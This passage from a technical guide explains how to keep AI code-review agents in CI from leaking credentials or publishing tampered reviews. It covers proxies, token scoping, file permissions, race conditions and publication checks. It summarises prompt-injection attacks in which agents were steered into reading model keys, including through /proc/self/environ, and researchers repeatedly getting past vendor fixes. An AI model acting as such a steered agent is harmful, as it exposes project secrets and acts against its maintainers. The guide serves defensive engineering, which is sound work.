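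Filtering credentials out of a child process's environment doesn't protect them if the child can read its parent's environment. The launcher has to hide the parent from the child, run the parent under a different user or, best of all, never give the parent the credentials.

Anthropic's and Google's fixes left credentials within the agent's reach. Anthropic blocked `ps`, which lists running processes, but other programs can read the same information. Guan told SecurityWeek that the attack should still work in principle with different text, although he had not attempted a full bypass. Google's new instructions leave the agent with the same tools and key, and work only if the model follows them. GitHub had published plans in March for an egress firewall in Actions and for secrets with a narrower scope. According to Claw Times, which cites The Register, none of the three vendors issued a public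 advisory, so users of older versions may not have known they needed to update.

Meged's later work on Anthropic's default workflow suggests that closing one route at a time is not enough to protect credentials. He told Help Net Security that each patch showed him where to look next, and that in the last round he recovered secrets without an outbound connection, a write or a log entry. He added that each fix did close the hole he had reported.

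These were demonstrations by skilled researchers and don't show how often such attacks happen. A first-time contributor also couldn't have repeated all of them in every repository, because GitHub withholds secrets from some workflows that a stranger can start.

### Google's Gemini CLI advisory

On 24 April 2026, Google published an advisory for Gemini CLI, its command-line coding agent, with the maximum CVSS score of 10.0. The advisory, *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* (GitHub Advisory Database, 2026), describes two flaws.

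The first concerned project settings. When Gemini CLI ran without a user present, it automatically trusted the project folder and loaded configuration and environment variables from it. In a workflow that reviews strangers' pull requests, the contributor supplies that folder and could set variables that made the machine run his code. The Hacker News (2026) quotes Novee Security, Meged's employer, as saying that the commands ran on the host before the agent's sandbox had started. At that point they could read whatever the job held. Emptying the environment before launch gives little protection if the harness then fills it from the contributor's files.

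The second flaw was in Gemini CLI's `--yolo` mode, which runs tools without asking. The mode ignored detailed limits on shell commands, so an outsider could use prompt injection to run any command, even in a project that had allowed only `echo`.

Google fixed both in version 0.39.1. Gemini CLI now requires explicit trust before it loads a project's settings, and it checks the list of permitted commands in `--yolo` mode. The Hacker News reported that the flaw had no CVE identifier, the number security tools use to track a vulnerability, but Corgea's *Gemini CLI* lists it as CVE-2026-12537.

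Updating may not be enough. The new version stops loading project settings in existing workflows, and Google tells owners to turn loading back on by setting `GEMINI_TRUST_WORKSPACE` to `true`. If the workflow handles untrusted input, they should first harden it according to Google's guidance. A maintainer who sets the variable only to fix a broken pipeline, without hardening it first, brings back the automatic trust.

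### A proxy that adds the model key

The harness needs to reach the model service, but it doesn't need the key. GitHub's Agent Workflow Firewall (AWF), which sets up the containers for Agentic Workflows, keeps the two apart. According to AWF's *Authentication Architecture*, a request to the model takes this route:

1. At startup, AWF gives the model key only to the container that runs the API proxy.
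2. AWF gives the agent's container the proxy's local address, which the usual client libraries then use in place of the vendor's.
3. The agent sends its request to the proxy without a key.
4. The proxy removes any authentication headers in the request, adds the real key and forwards the request through a firewall that permits only listed domains.

Removing any headers the agent sets prevents a manipulated agent from sending requests with an attacker's key. Those requests would put the prompts, and everything in them, in the attacker's account.

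Docker's sandboxes work similarly. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a proxy on the host that overwrites the authentication header, while the sandbox holds only a placeholder. The egress proxy in the example can do the same, since it already decrypts requests to the model service. Many harnesses refuse to start without a key, so the launcher adds a placeholder after `--clearenv`:

```bash
--setenv OPENAI_API_KEY placeholder   # the egress proxy adds the real key
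```

A real key should never appear in such an option, because other processes on the machine can usually read a program's command line.

OpenAI's Codex action, a ready-made step for GitHub Actions, runs its proxy on the same machine as the agent. According to OpenAI, the proxy reads the API key from standard input, tries to keep it from being swapped to disk, and accepts only POST requests to `/v1/responses`. An agent with administrator rights could still read the key from the proxy's memory, and the default user on GitHub's Linux machines can get those rights through `sudo`. By default, the action therefore removes `sudo` access before it starts Codex and doesn't restore it during the job. OpenAI's *Codex GitHub Action* documentation warns that the `read-only` strategy does not protect secrets by itself, because Codex keeps its elevated privileges. On Windows, the action supports only the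 `unsafe` strategy.

OpenClaw also lists a proxy as one of several authentication modes ClawSweeper can use to reach the model. OpenClaw says its production reviewers remove Codex, OpenAI and GitHub write credentials before they invoke the model. Local reviews instead use the maintainer's own Codex login.

A proxy stops the agent from copying the key but not from using it. GitHub cautions that its API proxy does not check which program in the agent's container is calling, so a contributor's test could also call the model. Strangers can benefit without stealing the key, too. OpenAI describes a project that lets anyone trigger the action and suddenly receives many issues about mining Bitcoin, from people who want answers at the project's expense.

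By default, only people with write access to the repository can start the Codex action, and *The Official Codex GitHub Action* (Vaughan, 2026) advises against ever opening it to everyone. An agent that reviews code from unknown contributors can't keep that protection in full. Its maintainer should use a separate key with a spending limit, cap the requests in each run, and allow requests only to the model endpoint, because the same key may also give access to other parts of the account, such as uploaded files.

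### Creating tokens late and letting them expire soon

OpenClaw creates ClawSweeper's write credentials only after Codex has exited, so a steered agent can't leak them while it runs. The credentials are tokens from a GitHub App, an identity that GitHub provides for programs. OpenClaw uses the App's private key only in the steps that create tokens.

In GitHub Actions, credentials remain within the agent's reach if a later step of the same job posts the review. The program that runs the job receives the job's secrets at the start and keeps them in memory, and a process left behind by the agent could wait for the next token. A separate job on GitHub's machines gets a new virtual machine and its own token. Agentic Workflows divides the work this way, and the job that posts a comment can write to issues but not to code.

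OpenAI has published two versions of a sample review workflow that give the agent's job different permissions. In the *Codex GitHub Action* README, the agent's job can only read the repository, and a second job has permission to post. In the newer documentation, the agent's job also has write access to pull requests. That sample fetches the code with version 5 of `actions/checkout`, which saves the token in the checkout by default, so Codex could find a token that can post comments. A maintainer who copies the newer sample should move the write permission to the posting job and stop `actions/checkout` from saving the token.

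Creating the token late does not remove the risk that the publisher will use its write credential to publish text written by a steered agent, so the publisher has to check the text first.

Expiry offers limited protection during an attack because a script needs only seconds to use a stolen token, but it does make a token harmless if someone finds it in an old log. ClawSweeper stops a review after ten minutes, but its read-only token can last for an hour, so a stolen copy may remain valid for 50 minutes after the agent exits. GitHub lets a program revoke an App's token early, and the launcher should do that as soon as the agent exits.

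Short lifetimes also complicate long jobs. ClawSweeper closes at most 40 items with one token, then queues another run with a new one.

Giving a credential a narrow scope limits the damage even within those first seconds. For agents that run in a customer's own environment, OpenAI provides a key that can only connect the environment to OpenAI's service. Code written by the agent can read this key but can't use it to authorise any other request.

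AWF can avoid using a permanent model key when the model runs on a cloud service. The API proxy obtains a short-lived identity token from GitHub and exchanges it for temporary cloud credentials, which it renews after 75% of their lifetime. GitHub normally sets environment variables that let a job request these identity tokens, so AWF also keeps those variables out of the agent's container.

### Token permissions and triggers in GitHub Actions

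For every job, GitHub creates a token called `GITHUB_TOKEN` that is valid for the repository in which the workflow runs. The `permissions` setting determines what the job can read or write with it. Once a workflow lists any permission, all the others are off. If it lists none, the repository's default applies, which may include write access in older projects.

For the example, the relevant parts of a workflow could look like this:

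```yaml
permissions: {}                       # no access unless a job asks for it

jobs:
  review:
    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    permissions:
      contents: read                  # source code
      pull-requests: read             # description, discussion and diff
    steps:
      - uses: actions/checkout@v6
        with:
          persist-credentials: false  # save no token for Git
      # the launcher runs the sandboxed agent here

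  publish:
    needs: review                     # start after the review job
    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    permissions:
      pull-requests: write            # post the review
    # the publisher's steps go here
```

The event that starts the workflow can reduce these permissions further and decides whether the job has access to stored secrets, such as the model key. These are the defaults for a public repository:

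| Event | Source of the workflow file | Stored secrets | Token |
|---|---|---|---|
| `pull_request` from a fork | The contributor's version | None | Read-only at most |
| `pull_request` from a branch in the repository | That branch | Available | As `permissions` allows |
| `pull_request_target` | The main branch | Available | As `permissions` allows |
| `issues` and `issue_comment` | The main branch | Available | As `permissions` allows |
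| `workflow_run` (after another workflow) | The main branch | Available | As `permissions` allows |

The first row is strict because the contributor can rewrite the workflow itself. In the other rows, the workflow file comes from people who can already write to the repository, but this does not protect an agent from hostile text. Anyone can open or comment on an issue in a public repository, and Guan reached the Gemini key that way without a fork.

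For pull requests from forks, Vaughan recommends two workflows connected by `workflow_run`. The first runs under `pull_request`, without secrets, and gathers material. The second then runs with access to the secrets. The contributor can change the first workflow, so the second must treat every file it receives as untrusted, including the one that names the pull request to review. The second workflow also has the model key in the same job as an agent that reads the contributor's text, so the key should still be kept in a proxy.

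Agentic Workflows avoids much of the problem by not running for outside contributors by default. According to GitHub's *Security Best Practices*, its `pull_request` workflows skip forks by default, and workflows run only for users who have at least write access. Both rules exclude the contributor in the example. A maintainer can let any user trigger a workflow by setting `roles: all`, which GitHub describes as high risk in public repositories.

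### No token or a read-only token

GitHub wanted the agents in Agentic Workflows to have no access to secrets, because a manipulated agent could find and publish them. The agents can still read issues and code through GitHub's MCP server, which runs in a separate container with its own token.

In practice the separation may be incomplete. The diagram in GitHub's blog post places the GitHub token with the MCP server, but AWF's documentation shows a `GITHUB_TOKEN` in the agent's container. AWF includes a library that is meant to hide the token by intercepting requests for the variable. At the first request, the library copies the value and removes the variable from the environment, then uses the copy for later requests. According to the documentation, `/proc` no longer shows the token afterwards. This is doubtful because the published code only removes the variable, which would leave the original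 text in memory. The library also does not work for programs that bypass the standard function for reading variables, including many written in Go. A project that uses AWF should check its own containers with a harmless test value.

OpenClaw gives ClawSweeper's agent a short-lived, read-only token for the contents, issues and pull requests of the repository under review. It does so because GitHub allows far fewer requests without a token, and a reviewer that looks up related issues could run out.

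For a public repository, this is a reasonable choice. A stranger who steals the token can't change anything and can read only what is already public. He could still use up the project's request limit and delay other reviews until the token expires.

Even a read-only token needs protection if the repository is private, because anyone who has it can copy the source code, history and internal discussion within minutes, long before it expires. A public project can have the same problem if its App is also installed on private repositories, such as one where maintainers prepare security fixes. The token covers every repository in the App's installation unless the launcher requests a token limited to one repository.

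GitHub automatically turns on lockdown mode when a workflow in a public repository uses a custom token for the MCP server. The server then returns only items written by people with push access. This keeps out most strangers' text, but it would also hide the pull request the agent is supposed to review, so the launcher would have to supply the pull request another way.

The example needs neither arrangement, because the launcher has already fetched the source, the diff and the discussion. If the agent has to look up an older issue, the egress proxy can add a read-only token to only that kind of request. This gives the project the higher request limit that OpenClaw wanted and keeps the token out of the sandbox. In a private repository, the proxy protects only the token. The agent can still read confidential code through the proxy and copy passages into its review, so the review file needs protection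 too.

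## Output files that only their owner can read or write

In the example pull request, the agent might find that the bug it noticed also exists in the released library. Its review would then describe how to attack the library's users before a fix exists. The review might also quote a password that the contributor committed by accident. Even a review that contains nothing sensitive has to reach the publisher unchanged.

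### Mode bits and the umask

Every file on a Unix system has an owner, which is a user account, and a group, which is a named set of accounts. The file's mode lists what the owner, the group's members and everyone else may do. Each of the three has a read bit (worth 4), a write bit (2) and an execute bit (1), which add up to one octal digit. Mode 0644 lets the owner read and write the file and everyone else only read it. Mode 0600 lets only the owner read or write it.

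For a directory, the read bit lets a process list the names, the write bit lets it create, rename and delete entries, and the execute bit lets it reach the files inside. Replacing a file therefore requires write permission on its directory, not on the file itself. Other accounts that can write to the directory can't read an owner-only review there, but they can usually delete it and save a different one under the same name.

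A program requests a mode when it creates a file. The kernel then clears from that mode every bit set in the umask, a value each process inherits from the program that started it. Most programs request 0666, and many systems use a umask of 022.

```text
requested   0666   110 110 110
umask        022   000 010 010
result      0644   110 100 100

requested   0666   110 110 110
umask        077   000 111 111
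result      0600   110 000 000
```

If the launcher sets its umask to 077 before it starts the agent, ordinary programs in the sandbox create owner-only files by default. The agent can still change its own umask or loosen a file's mode, so the launcher should also give the run directory, `/srv/review/run-1`, mode 0700. Other accounts then can't reach anything inside it, whatever modes the agent sets.

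### Files that become private too late

A common mistake is to create a file and then run `chmod 600` on it. Under a umask of 022, the file starts at 0644, so another account can open it before `chmod` runs. The kernel checks permissions when a process opens a file, so a program that opens it while it is still empty can read the entire review as it is written, even after `chmod` runs. The gap may last only microseconds, but a program can watch the directory for new files and try again at every run.

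Requesting 0600 at creation closes this gap only if the file is new. When a program overwrites an existing file, the kernel ignores the requested mode, so a review written over an old file at 0644 is readable by everyone. According to its documentation, the small Go package *safeio* (pkg.go.dev, 2026) avoids both problems by writing the data to a new temporary file at 0600 and renaming that file over the old one. The umask can only remove permissions, so the data is private from the start, and the new file does not inherit the old one's mode.

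### Storing the review

The launcher can use the same method to store the finished review in a directory that the sandbox never contained. This takes seven system calls:

1. `mkdir` creates a directory with mode 0700. It fails if anything already has that name, including a link.
2. `open` opens the directory. The later steps refer to this open directory, so they still reach it if somebody changes the path.
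3. `openat` creates a temporary file at 0600 with the flags `O_CREAT` and `O_EXCL`, which together mean that the call fails if the name exists.
4. `write` stores the data.
5. `fsync` waits until the data is on the disk.
6. `renameat` gives the file its final name.
7. `fsync` on the directory makes the new name survive a crash.

In Python, the sequence looks like this:

```python
import os

def store(run, data):
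    os.mkdir(f"{run}/private", 0o700)
    d = os.open(f"{run}/private",
                os.O_RDONLY | os.O_DIRECTORY | os.O_NOFOLLOW)
    fd = os.open("review.tmp",
                 os.O_WRONLY | os.O_CREAT | os.O_EXCL | os.O_NOFOLLOW,
                 0o600, dir_fd=d)
    with os.fdopen(fd, "wb") as f:
        f.write(data)
        f.flush()                      # hand Python's buffer to the kernel
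        os.fsync(f.fileno())           # wait for the disk
    os.rename("review.tmp", "review.json", src_dir_fd=d, dst_dir_fd=d)
    os.fsync(d)
    os.close(d)
```

`O_NOFOLLOW` makes the call fail if the last part of the path is a symbolic link. It is only a second safeguard for the new file, because exclusive creation on Unix never follows such a link. On Windows, however, Go's version of this call used to create a file at the target of a broken symbolic link, according to GCVE's *GHSA-jw54-c8rr-pjpq* (2025).

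The rename is atomic, so the publisher finds either a complete review or none. This holds only within one filesystem, and Linux also refuses to rename a file from one mount to another, even if both are mounts of the same filesystem. The agent therefore can't prepare its review in `/tmp` and rename it into `/work/out`. `mv` would appear to work, but it would copy the data, and a crash during the copy could leave half a review under the final name.

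### Links and check-then-use races

The launcher also has to read the agent's file safely, because the agent controls everything in `/work/out`. A steered agent could leave a symbolic link there under the expected name, pointing to a file in the maintainer's home directory. That file doesn't exist inside the sandbox, but the launcher runs outside, where it does. A launcher that follows symbolic links would pass the maintainer's file to the publisher as the review.

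A hard link is a second name for the same file, so `O_NOFOLLOW` doesn't detect it, but a link count above one reveals it. In the example, the agent can't create a hard link to a file in the source tree or outside the sandbox, because hard links can't cross mounts. Without separate mounts, it could link to another file that its account may access.

If the launcher checks the path for links and then opens it, a process that is still running could swap the file between the two steps. CIRCL's *Common Weakness Enumeration* defines this type of flaw as a check whose result can become invalid before the program uses the resource. GCVE's *GHSA-W853-JP5J-5J7F* (2025) describes this flaw in filelock, a library that programs use to take turns with a file. Filelock checked whether its lock file existed and then opened it in a way that erased its contents. If another local user put a link at that path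 between the two steps, filelock erased the contents of the file that the link pointed to.

The cure is to open the file first and then examine what is open:

```python
import os, stat

LIMIT = 1_048_576                      # 1 MiB

def collect(run):
    fd = os.open(f"{run}/out/review.json",
                 os.O_RDONLY | os.O_NOFOLLOW | os.O_NONBLOCK)
    with os.fdopen(fd, "rb") as f:
        info = os.fstat(f.fileno())
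        if not stat.S_ISREG(info.st_mode) or info.st_nlink != 1:
            raise ValueError("not an ordinary file with one name")
        data = f.read(LIMIT + 1)
    if len(data) > LIMIT:
        raise ValueError("review too large")
    return data
```

`fstat` describes the file that is already open, so swapping the name afterward doesn't affect the check. `O_NONBLOCK` keeps the launcher from waiting forever for a writer if the agent leaves a named pipe instead of a file. In the example, the file must be directly in `out`. If the agent could choose a subdirectory, the launcher would have to check every part of the path, because `O_NOFOLLOW` rejects a symbolic link only in the last part.

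OpenClaw packages these precautions in fs-safe, a library for Node.js programs that handle untrusted path names. Many programs confine a path by checking that it starts with the name of the permitted directory. OpenClaw objects that this validates only a string, not the file the program later opens. The check can also fail without a race, because `/srv/review/run-10` starts with `/srv/review/run-1`. When fs-safe reads a file, it refuses links where the system allows it and confirms that the open file is the one at the path before returning any data. When it writes a file, it holds on to the parent directory, replaces the file atomically and then checks where the data was written. It can also reject hard links, but OpenClaw calls that an extra layer because the link count depends on the platform.

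OpenClaw's own code had such a race. GitLab's *GHSA-x82f-27x3-q89c* (2026), published on 2 March with a severity of 7.5 out of 10, concerns a function that was supposed to write only below a given directory. Someone who controlled a link in the path could redirect the link after the function resolved the path but before it wrote. The function checked the location again, but according to Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-25136 · Npm · Openclaw* (2026), by then it could already have created a file outside the directory or emptied one there. Version 2026.3.1 opens existing files without emptying them, creates missing files in exclusive mode, and erases old contents only after verifying the open file.

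Two of the advisories that followed match steps in the sequence above. According to GitLab's *GHSA-mj4p-rc52-m843* (2026), OpenClaw verified the destination but did not tie the temporary file to a verified directory, which step 3 does with the open directory. In OSV's *GHSA-xvx8-77m6-gwg6* (2026), the final move (step 6) still used the raw path. Later that month, GitLab's *GHSA-7xr2-q9vf-x4r5* (2026) reported that an earlier patch had added link checks to two functions but missed two others in the same file. In April, version 2026.4.22 fixed another race in sandbox writes, according to Corgea's *Duplicate Advisory*. These repeated flaws are a good reason to put file access into one library, where a fix reaches every caller.

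On Linux, fs-safe can use `openat2`, a system call that can make the kernel refuse any path that leaves a given directory. According to OpenClaw's *Secure file operations*, this requires a compiled helper. If the helper is missing, many operations fall back to weaker checks in the default `auto` mode but fail in `require` mode. An unattended reviewer should use `require` so that it fails closed.

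### When a stranger's test runs under the same account

Owner-only permissions do not separate two programs that run under the same account. "Owner" in a file's mode means the account, so the kernel gives a test that the agent started the same access to the file as the agent. If the contributor's test runs in the agent's sandbox, it can read and rewrite an owner-only review. Making the file read-only gives little protection, because any program running under the owner's account can make it writable again.

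The same limit affected Anthropic's Claude Code GitHub Action. Microsoft (2026) found that the action could expose a workflow's secrets while it processed untrusted issues and pull requests. Linux lets only the owner read `/proc/self/environ`, which holds a process's starting environment. According to VPN Central's *Microsoft Warns Claude Code GitHub Action Could Leak CI/CD Secrets*, the agent's file-reading tool could read the Anthropic key from that file. The file's mode allowed this because the tool ran as the owner. Anthropic has since blocked the tool from reading such files.

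There are four common remedies, and they differ in what the test can still do. The first row shows the problem.

| Arrangement | Can the test read the review? | Can the test change it? |
|---|---|---|
| Owner-only file, same account and sandbox | Yes | Yes |
| Pipe to the launcher, same account and sandbox | Possibly, through the agent's open files | It can add text, but can't alter what the launcher has received |
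| File that the launcher opened, same account and sandbox | Usually, through the agent's open files | Yes, until the launcher locks the contents |
| Separate accounts | No | No |
| Writable mount that only the agent's sandbox contains | No | No |

The agent can print its review to a pipe that the launcher reads, so the sandbox needs no output file. The launcher can count the bytes and stop the agent if its output exceeds the limit. But programs that the agent starts normally inherit its standard output, so the harness has to capture each command's output separately. Otherwise, a test's messages could appear in the middle of the review. Even with separate capture, a process can usually reach another process's open files through `/proc` if both run under the same account. The launcher must also treat an early end of the stream as a failure, because an incomplete review may look favorable.

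The launcher can instead create the file itself and pass the agent a file descriptor, the number a process uses to refer to an open file. This prevents the link attacks because the agent never chooses a path. The agent can still overwrite what it has written, and so can any program that inherits the descriptor. On Linux, the launcher can create the file in memory with `memfd_create` and seal it once the agent has finished. The kernel then rejects all writes, even from a process that still has the file open.

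Separate accounts make the mode bits work as intended, because the review and the test then have different owners. Switching accounts requires administrator rights or a service manager such as systemd, which can create a temporary account for a single run. The launcher may then not be allowed to read the output file. Combining separate accounts with a pipe solves this more safely than running the launcher as root, because a root launcher that follows an untrusted link can expose any file on the machine. Two reviews that run at the same time need separate accounts, or each agent can read the other's output.

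The example already uses the last arrangement in the table, because its tests run in a separate sandbox without `/work/out`. This works even though both sandboxes use the launcher's account, and it takes the least work on a machine that already has bubblewrap. OpenClaw likewise tells users not to rely on fs-safe against hostile local users, and to use separate accounts, separate machines or a sandbox.

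Each sandbox must have its own writable directory. GCVE's *Common Weakness Enumeration* includes a 2024 flaw in runc, the program that starts containers for Docker and others. When two containers shared a directory, a race between them could make runc create empty files elsewhere on the host. The launcher should wait until every process in the sandbox has ended before it collects the review, because a background process could still be writing. It can check for remaining processes in the control group that caps the run's memory.

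### Root and mapped accounts

Root, the administrator account, ignores mode bits, so a shared server's administrators can read or change an owner-only file, as can anyone who can use `sudo` or Docker's socket on that server. Encrypting the file helps only if the key is on another machine, since root can also read the memory of running programs.

User namespaces complicate file ownership because an account can have one user ID inside the namespace and another outside. Bubblewrap normally maps only the account that started it, so a file that the agent creates in the example belongs to the launcher's account on the host, and the launcher can read it when its mode is 0600. A process that appears as root inside such a namespace gains no extra access to files that belong to unmapped accounts.

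Podman, which can run containers without administrator rights, usually maps a whole range of accounts. Suppose the launcher runs as account 1000 and its range starts at 100000. Root in the container corresponds to account 1000 on the host, account 1 to 100000, and account *n* to 100000 + *n* − 1. If the agent runs as account 1000 in the container, its files belong to account 100999 on the host, and the launcher can't open a review file with mode 0600. Making the file readable by everyone would defeat the purpose. Podman's option `--userns=keep-id` keeps the launcher's account number the same inside and outside the container. Sending the review through a pipe also avoids the problem.

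### Backups and uploaded artifacts

A file's mode controls access only to that copy of the file. Backup programs often run as root so that they can read everything, and the backup server's rules then determine who can read the backup. Deleting the review from the reviewing machine does not delete the backup. The maintainer should exclude `/srv/review` from backups or keep it in memory, although the kernel may still write its contents to swap space on the disk.

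In GitHub Actions, the agent's job usually has to pass the review to the publisher's job as an artifact, a file that GitHub stores with the workflow run. GitHub's standard upload step packs artifacts into a zip file and discards the files' permission modes, so after the download files normally have mode 0644 and directories 0755. Packing the review into a tar archive first preserves its mode, but this matters little, because anyone signed in to GitHub can download artifacts from a public repository. A project that expects confidential findings can have the launcher encrypt the review with a public key and can give the private key only to the publisher's job.

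OpenClaw uploads each ClawSweeper review as an artifact with a SHA-256 hash, a short fingerprint that changes if the file changes. Before a publisher receives write tokens, a separate service checks the artifact's workflow run, list of files, sizes and hashes. This protects the review against changes in transit but doesn't stop others from reading it. The expected hash also has to be stored where the agent can't write, or a steered agent could replace both the review and its hash. In one of its tests, OpenClaw keeps commands, prompts and transcripts in temporary private files and uploads only counts and yes-or-no results.

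### Retention and size limits

A file that no longer exists can't leak, so the launcher should decide in advance what survives a run. When a maintainer runs ClawSweeper locally, there are three levels:

- `none`, the default, prints the result and removes the private working directory.
- `summary` keeps the report without the raw prompts and model output.
- `debug` keeps everything.

An older option for choosing an output directory still selects `debug`, so a maintainer who reuses an old command may be keeping more output than he realizes. Even `none` can leave files behind if the operating system kills the process, because ClawSweeper then cannot clean up. The launcher in the example should therefore also delete leftover run directories when it starts.

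Saved prompts can help explain why a review went wrong, but they contain everything the launcher put into them. Before ClawSweeper saves a diagnostic copy of a prompt from a review or repair run, it deletes the copy from the previous attempt, then scans the new prompt for credentials. It saves the prompt only if it passes the scan, in a file that only the owner can access.

ClawSweeper limits temporary output to 96 MiB and 256 files, and debug output to 1 GiB and 4,096 files. Files already at the destination count towards the limit. The hosted service keeps its artifacts for 90 days, which helps if someone disputes a review weeks later but is a long time to keep a review that quotes an unfixed security hole.

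According to OpenClaw, its caps are not a disk quota. Download and video tools can temporarily exceed them, and the caps don't cover files that the model writes on its own initiative. In the example, the small separate filesystem for `/work/out` limits the total size of such files, and the kernel can cap the size of any single file that a process writes (`ulimit -f`).

### Secrets in committed settings files

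Many secrets leave a developer's machine through programs that are allowed to read them. For example, when Claude Code asks for permission to run a command and the user chooses "Yes, and don't ask again", it saves the command, including any password in it, in `.claude/settings.local.json` inside the project.

Between 1 and 3 November 2026, the security company Apiiro examined 104,185 public copies of this file on GitHub. According to iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets*, 1,122 of them, or 1.1%, held at least one secret. Apiiro counted 1,379 different secrets, including 379 database passwords. Including older versions of the file, shared settings and saved chat transcripts, it found 2,539 secrets in 1,994 repositories. Apiiro did not test whether the secrets still worked, but one organisation confirmed that its key had been live.

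GitGuardian, another security company, counted everything that users had pushed since January 2025, including files they later deleted. Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026) reports 31,088 different credentials, of which 5,343 worked when GitGuardian detected them. The monthly number peaked at 12,535 in April 2026 and fell to 959 in October, and GitGuardian does not know why. The file also appears in public packages. TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026) describes a scan of about 46,500 packages, of which 428 contained the file and 30 exposed live credentials through it.

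Claude Code tries to prevent this by adding the file to the developer's personal Git ignore list. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* explains that this list stays on one machine and does not protect a clone elsewhere or a file that somebody has already committed. Boris Cherny, who heads Claude Code, argued that people must have created the exposed files by hand. GitGuardian's evidence makes that unlikely, because in the roughly 3,000 occurrences GitGuardian examined, every secret was in a rule with exactly the form that the permission prompt writes. In almost half of the repositories that Apiiro traced, Claude also co-authored a commit that changed the file.

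Mode 0600 would not have prevented any of these commits. Git runs under the developer's account, so it can read the developer's owner-only files. Git also stores only whether a file is executable, not its full mode, so a 0600 file becomes 0644 in a clone made under a umask of 022.

Keeping the file out of the repository helps. GitLab's *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* recommends an entry in the project's own `.gitignore`, which is copied along with the code, and a server rule that rejects any push adding a file of that name. The rule does not stop changes to a copy that Git already tracks, so a project has to remove existing copies first. Secret scanners are less reliable here because a password in a command looks like an ordinary word. The popular scanners gitleaks and TruffleHog both missed 215 of Apiiro's 1,122 files.

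The reviewer in the example can't leave such a file in the project, because its source tree is read-only and its home directory disappears after the run. Its review could still end up in a commit if the launcher stored it inside a checkout, where a maintainer might add it along with other new files. The run directory therefore belongs outside every repository. By default, ClawSweeper stores retained reports about local branches under `.git`, which Git never commits.

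## From the agent's output to a change in the repository

When the example run ends, the review is in an owner-only file on the maintainer's machine, where the contributor can't see it. The publisher posts it, because reading every review and pasting it in by hand would take up much of the time the agent saves the maintainer. Posting requires a write credential, so the publisher uses one on text that a stranger may have influenced.

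### The confused deputy

*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a compiler on a shared computer that could write to a system directory because it kept usage statistics there. The compiler also let users name a file for its debugging output. One user gave the name of the billing file in that directory, and the compiler overwrote it. The user had no permission to change that file, but the compiler did, and the operating system checked only the compiler's permission. Hardy called the compiler a confused deputy because it used its own authority for someone else's purpose.

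A publisher can have the same flaw. If the agent's output includes a pull request number and the publisher posts the review there, a stranger who manipulates the agent could make the project's bot comment on someone else's pull request, because the publisher's token probably allows comments on every pull request in the repository.

Hardy's remedy was to have the user pass the permission along with the file, so that the compiler would not use its own permission. An ordinary code host token can't be divided up this way for each request, but the publisher can get most of the benefit by taking the repository, pull request number and commit from the launcher's record of the run. The agent then supplies only the content of the review.

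GitHub accepts a review as a comment, an approval or a request for changes. The publisher in the example always posts a comment, because if it copied the agent's verdict into the review type, a stranger might obtain a formal approval from the project's bot.

A comment can also contain a command to another program. OpenClaw lets people start a ClawSweeper review by writing a command in a comment, and checks their repository permissions first. If another bot accepts commands from the publisher's account on the same basis, a command hidden in a review could trigger it. The publisher should remove commands that the project's bots recognise from reviews.

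### GitHub's safe outputs

Agentic Workflows has a general-purpose publisher called safe outputs. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026), which is still a working draft, sets out how a request becomes a change. Together with GitHub's description of the detection job, it gives this sequence:

1. The maintainer lists the types of change that the agent may request and a limit for each. GitHub's compiler, which turns the workflow into Actions jobs, creates one tool per type.
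2. The agent calls a tool. The safe-outputs server, which runs in a separate container, checks that the request has the right fields and adds it to a file. It then reports success to the agent, although nothing has changed on GitHub yet.
3. The agent ends, and its job uploads the file as an artifact.
4. A detection job without write access asks a model to look for leaked secrets and malicious code. If it finds any, the workflow stops.
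5. A job with write permission downloads the file. It checks the form and number of the requests, cleans their text, removes links to unlisted domains and checks the target repository.
6. The same job sends the remaining requests to GitHub.

For the example review, the maintainer could configure it like this:

```yaml
safe-outputs:
  allowed-domains: [github.com]                 # keep only these links
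  allowed-github-references: [example/library]  # write only here
  add-comment:
    max: 1
```

An agent that has found a bug then stages one request:

```json
{"type": "add_comment", "body": "src/header.c, line 88: reads one byte past the buffer if the line is empty."}
```

This request doesn't name a pull request. The maintainer has set no target, so the job comments on the pull request that triggered the workflow and adds a footer with a link to the run. In another run, a steered agent might stage this:

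```json
{"type": "add_comment", "target-repo": "example/website", "body": "The new release is ready."}
```

The job rejects it with error E004 because `example/website` is not on the list. The agent could not have closed the pull request instead, because it has no tool for that.

The maintainer should fill in the repository list even for a workflow that writes to one repository. One passage of GitHub's specification requires the job to refuse all requests for other repositories if there is no list, but under another passage an empty list imposes no restriction.

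To prevent the confused deputy problem, GitHub lets the agent choose which item to change only if the maintainer sets the target to `*`. Otherwise, the job uses the triggering item or a fixed number, and it must stop if its target differs from the authorised one. A maintainer can also give each type of change its own token, so the code that posts comments can't start other workflows.

The limits are all-or-nothing. If a workflow permits three new issues and the agent requests five, the job creates none. A stranger can therefore suppress an unwelcome review by getting the agent to make one request too many. Rejecting all five is still better than accepting the first three, because the maintainer sees an error and the first three might be spam. Other errors affect only the request that contains them.

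Removing secrets from the output is less dependable. GitHub Actions can mask secrets that the project has registered, because it knows their exact text. For other secrets, the job looks for strings that resemble credentials, which GitHub rates as only moderately effective because new formats get through. Guan's attack on Copilot got past such a scanner. Removing secrets from the output is therefore a backup to the main defense, which is keeping them away from the agent.

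A stranger's text could steer the detection job as well as the agent. According to GitHub, the job uses the same AI engine as the workflow and reads the agent's output and the workflow's original context, either of which may contain such text. But the job can only pass or block the output. If it wrongly passes a harmful request, the project is no worse off than without the job, as long as the maintainer has not loosened the other checks because of it.

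A maintainer who is unsure about a configuration can set `staged: true`. The job then shows what it would have changed and leaves the repository alone.

### ClawSweeper's publication path

ClawSweeper handles only reviews, labels and closures, so its publisher can check more than whether a request is well formed.

Codex writes its decision to a `review_record`, whose fields have fixed types. OpenClaw reads decisions only from this record. If the record is missing or unreadable, ClawSweeper skips the item and requires a new review. It does not search the written report for a decision, because the report can quote the contributor's description and a program looking for the word "close" might find it there.

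ClawSweeper uploads the result with hashes that tie it to the run. Before a publisher gets write tokens, a service checks the hashes, the target, the decision and the item's place in the review queue, so a genuine review of one pull request can't appear under another. If the item's queue entry is out of date, ClawSweeper drops the result. If publication fails for a technical reason, ClawSweeper can retry with the same result without rerunning Codex.

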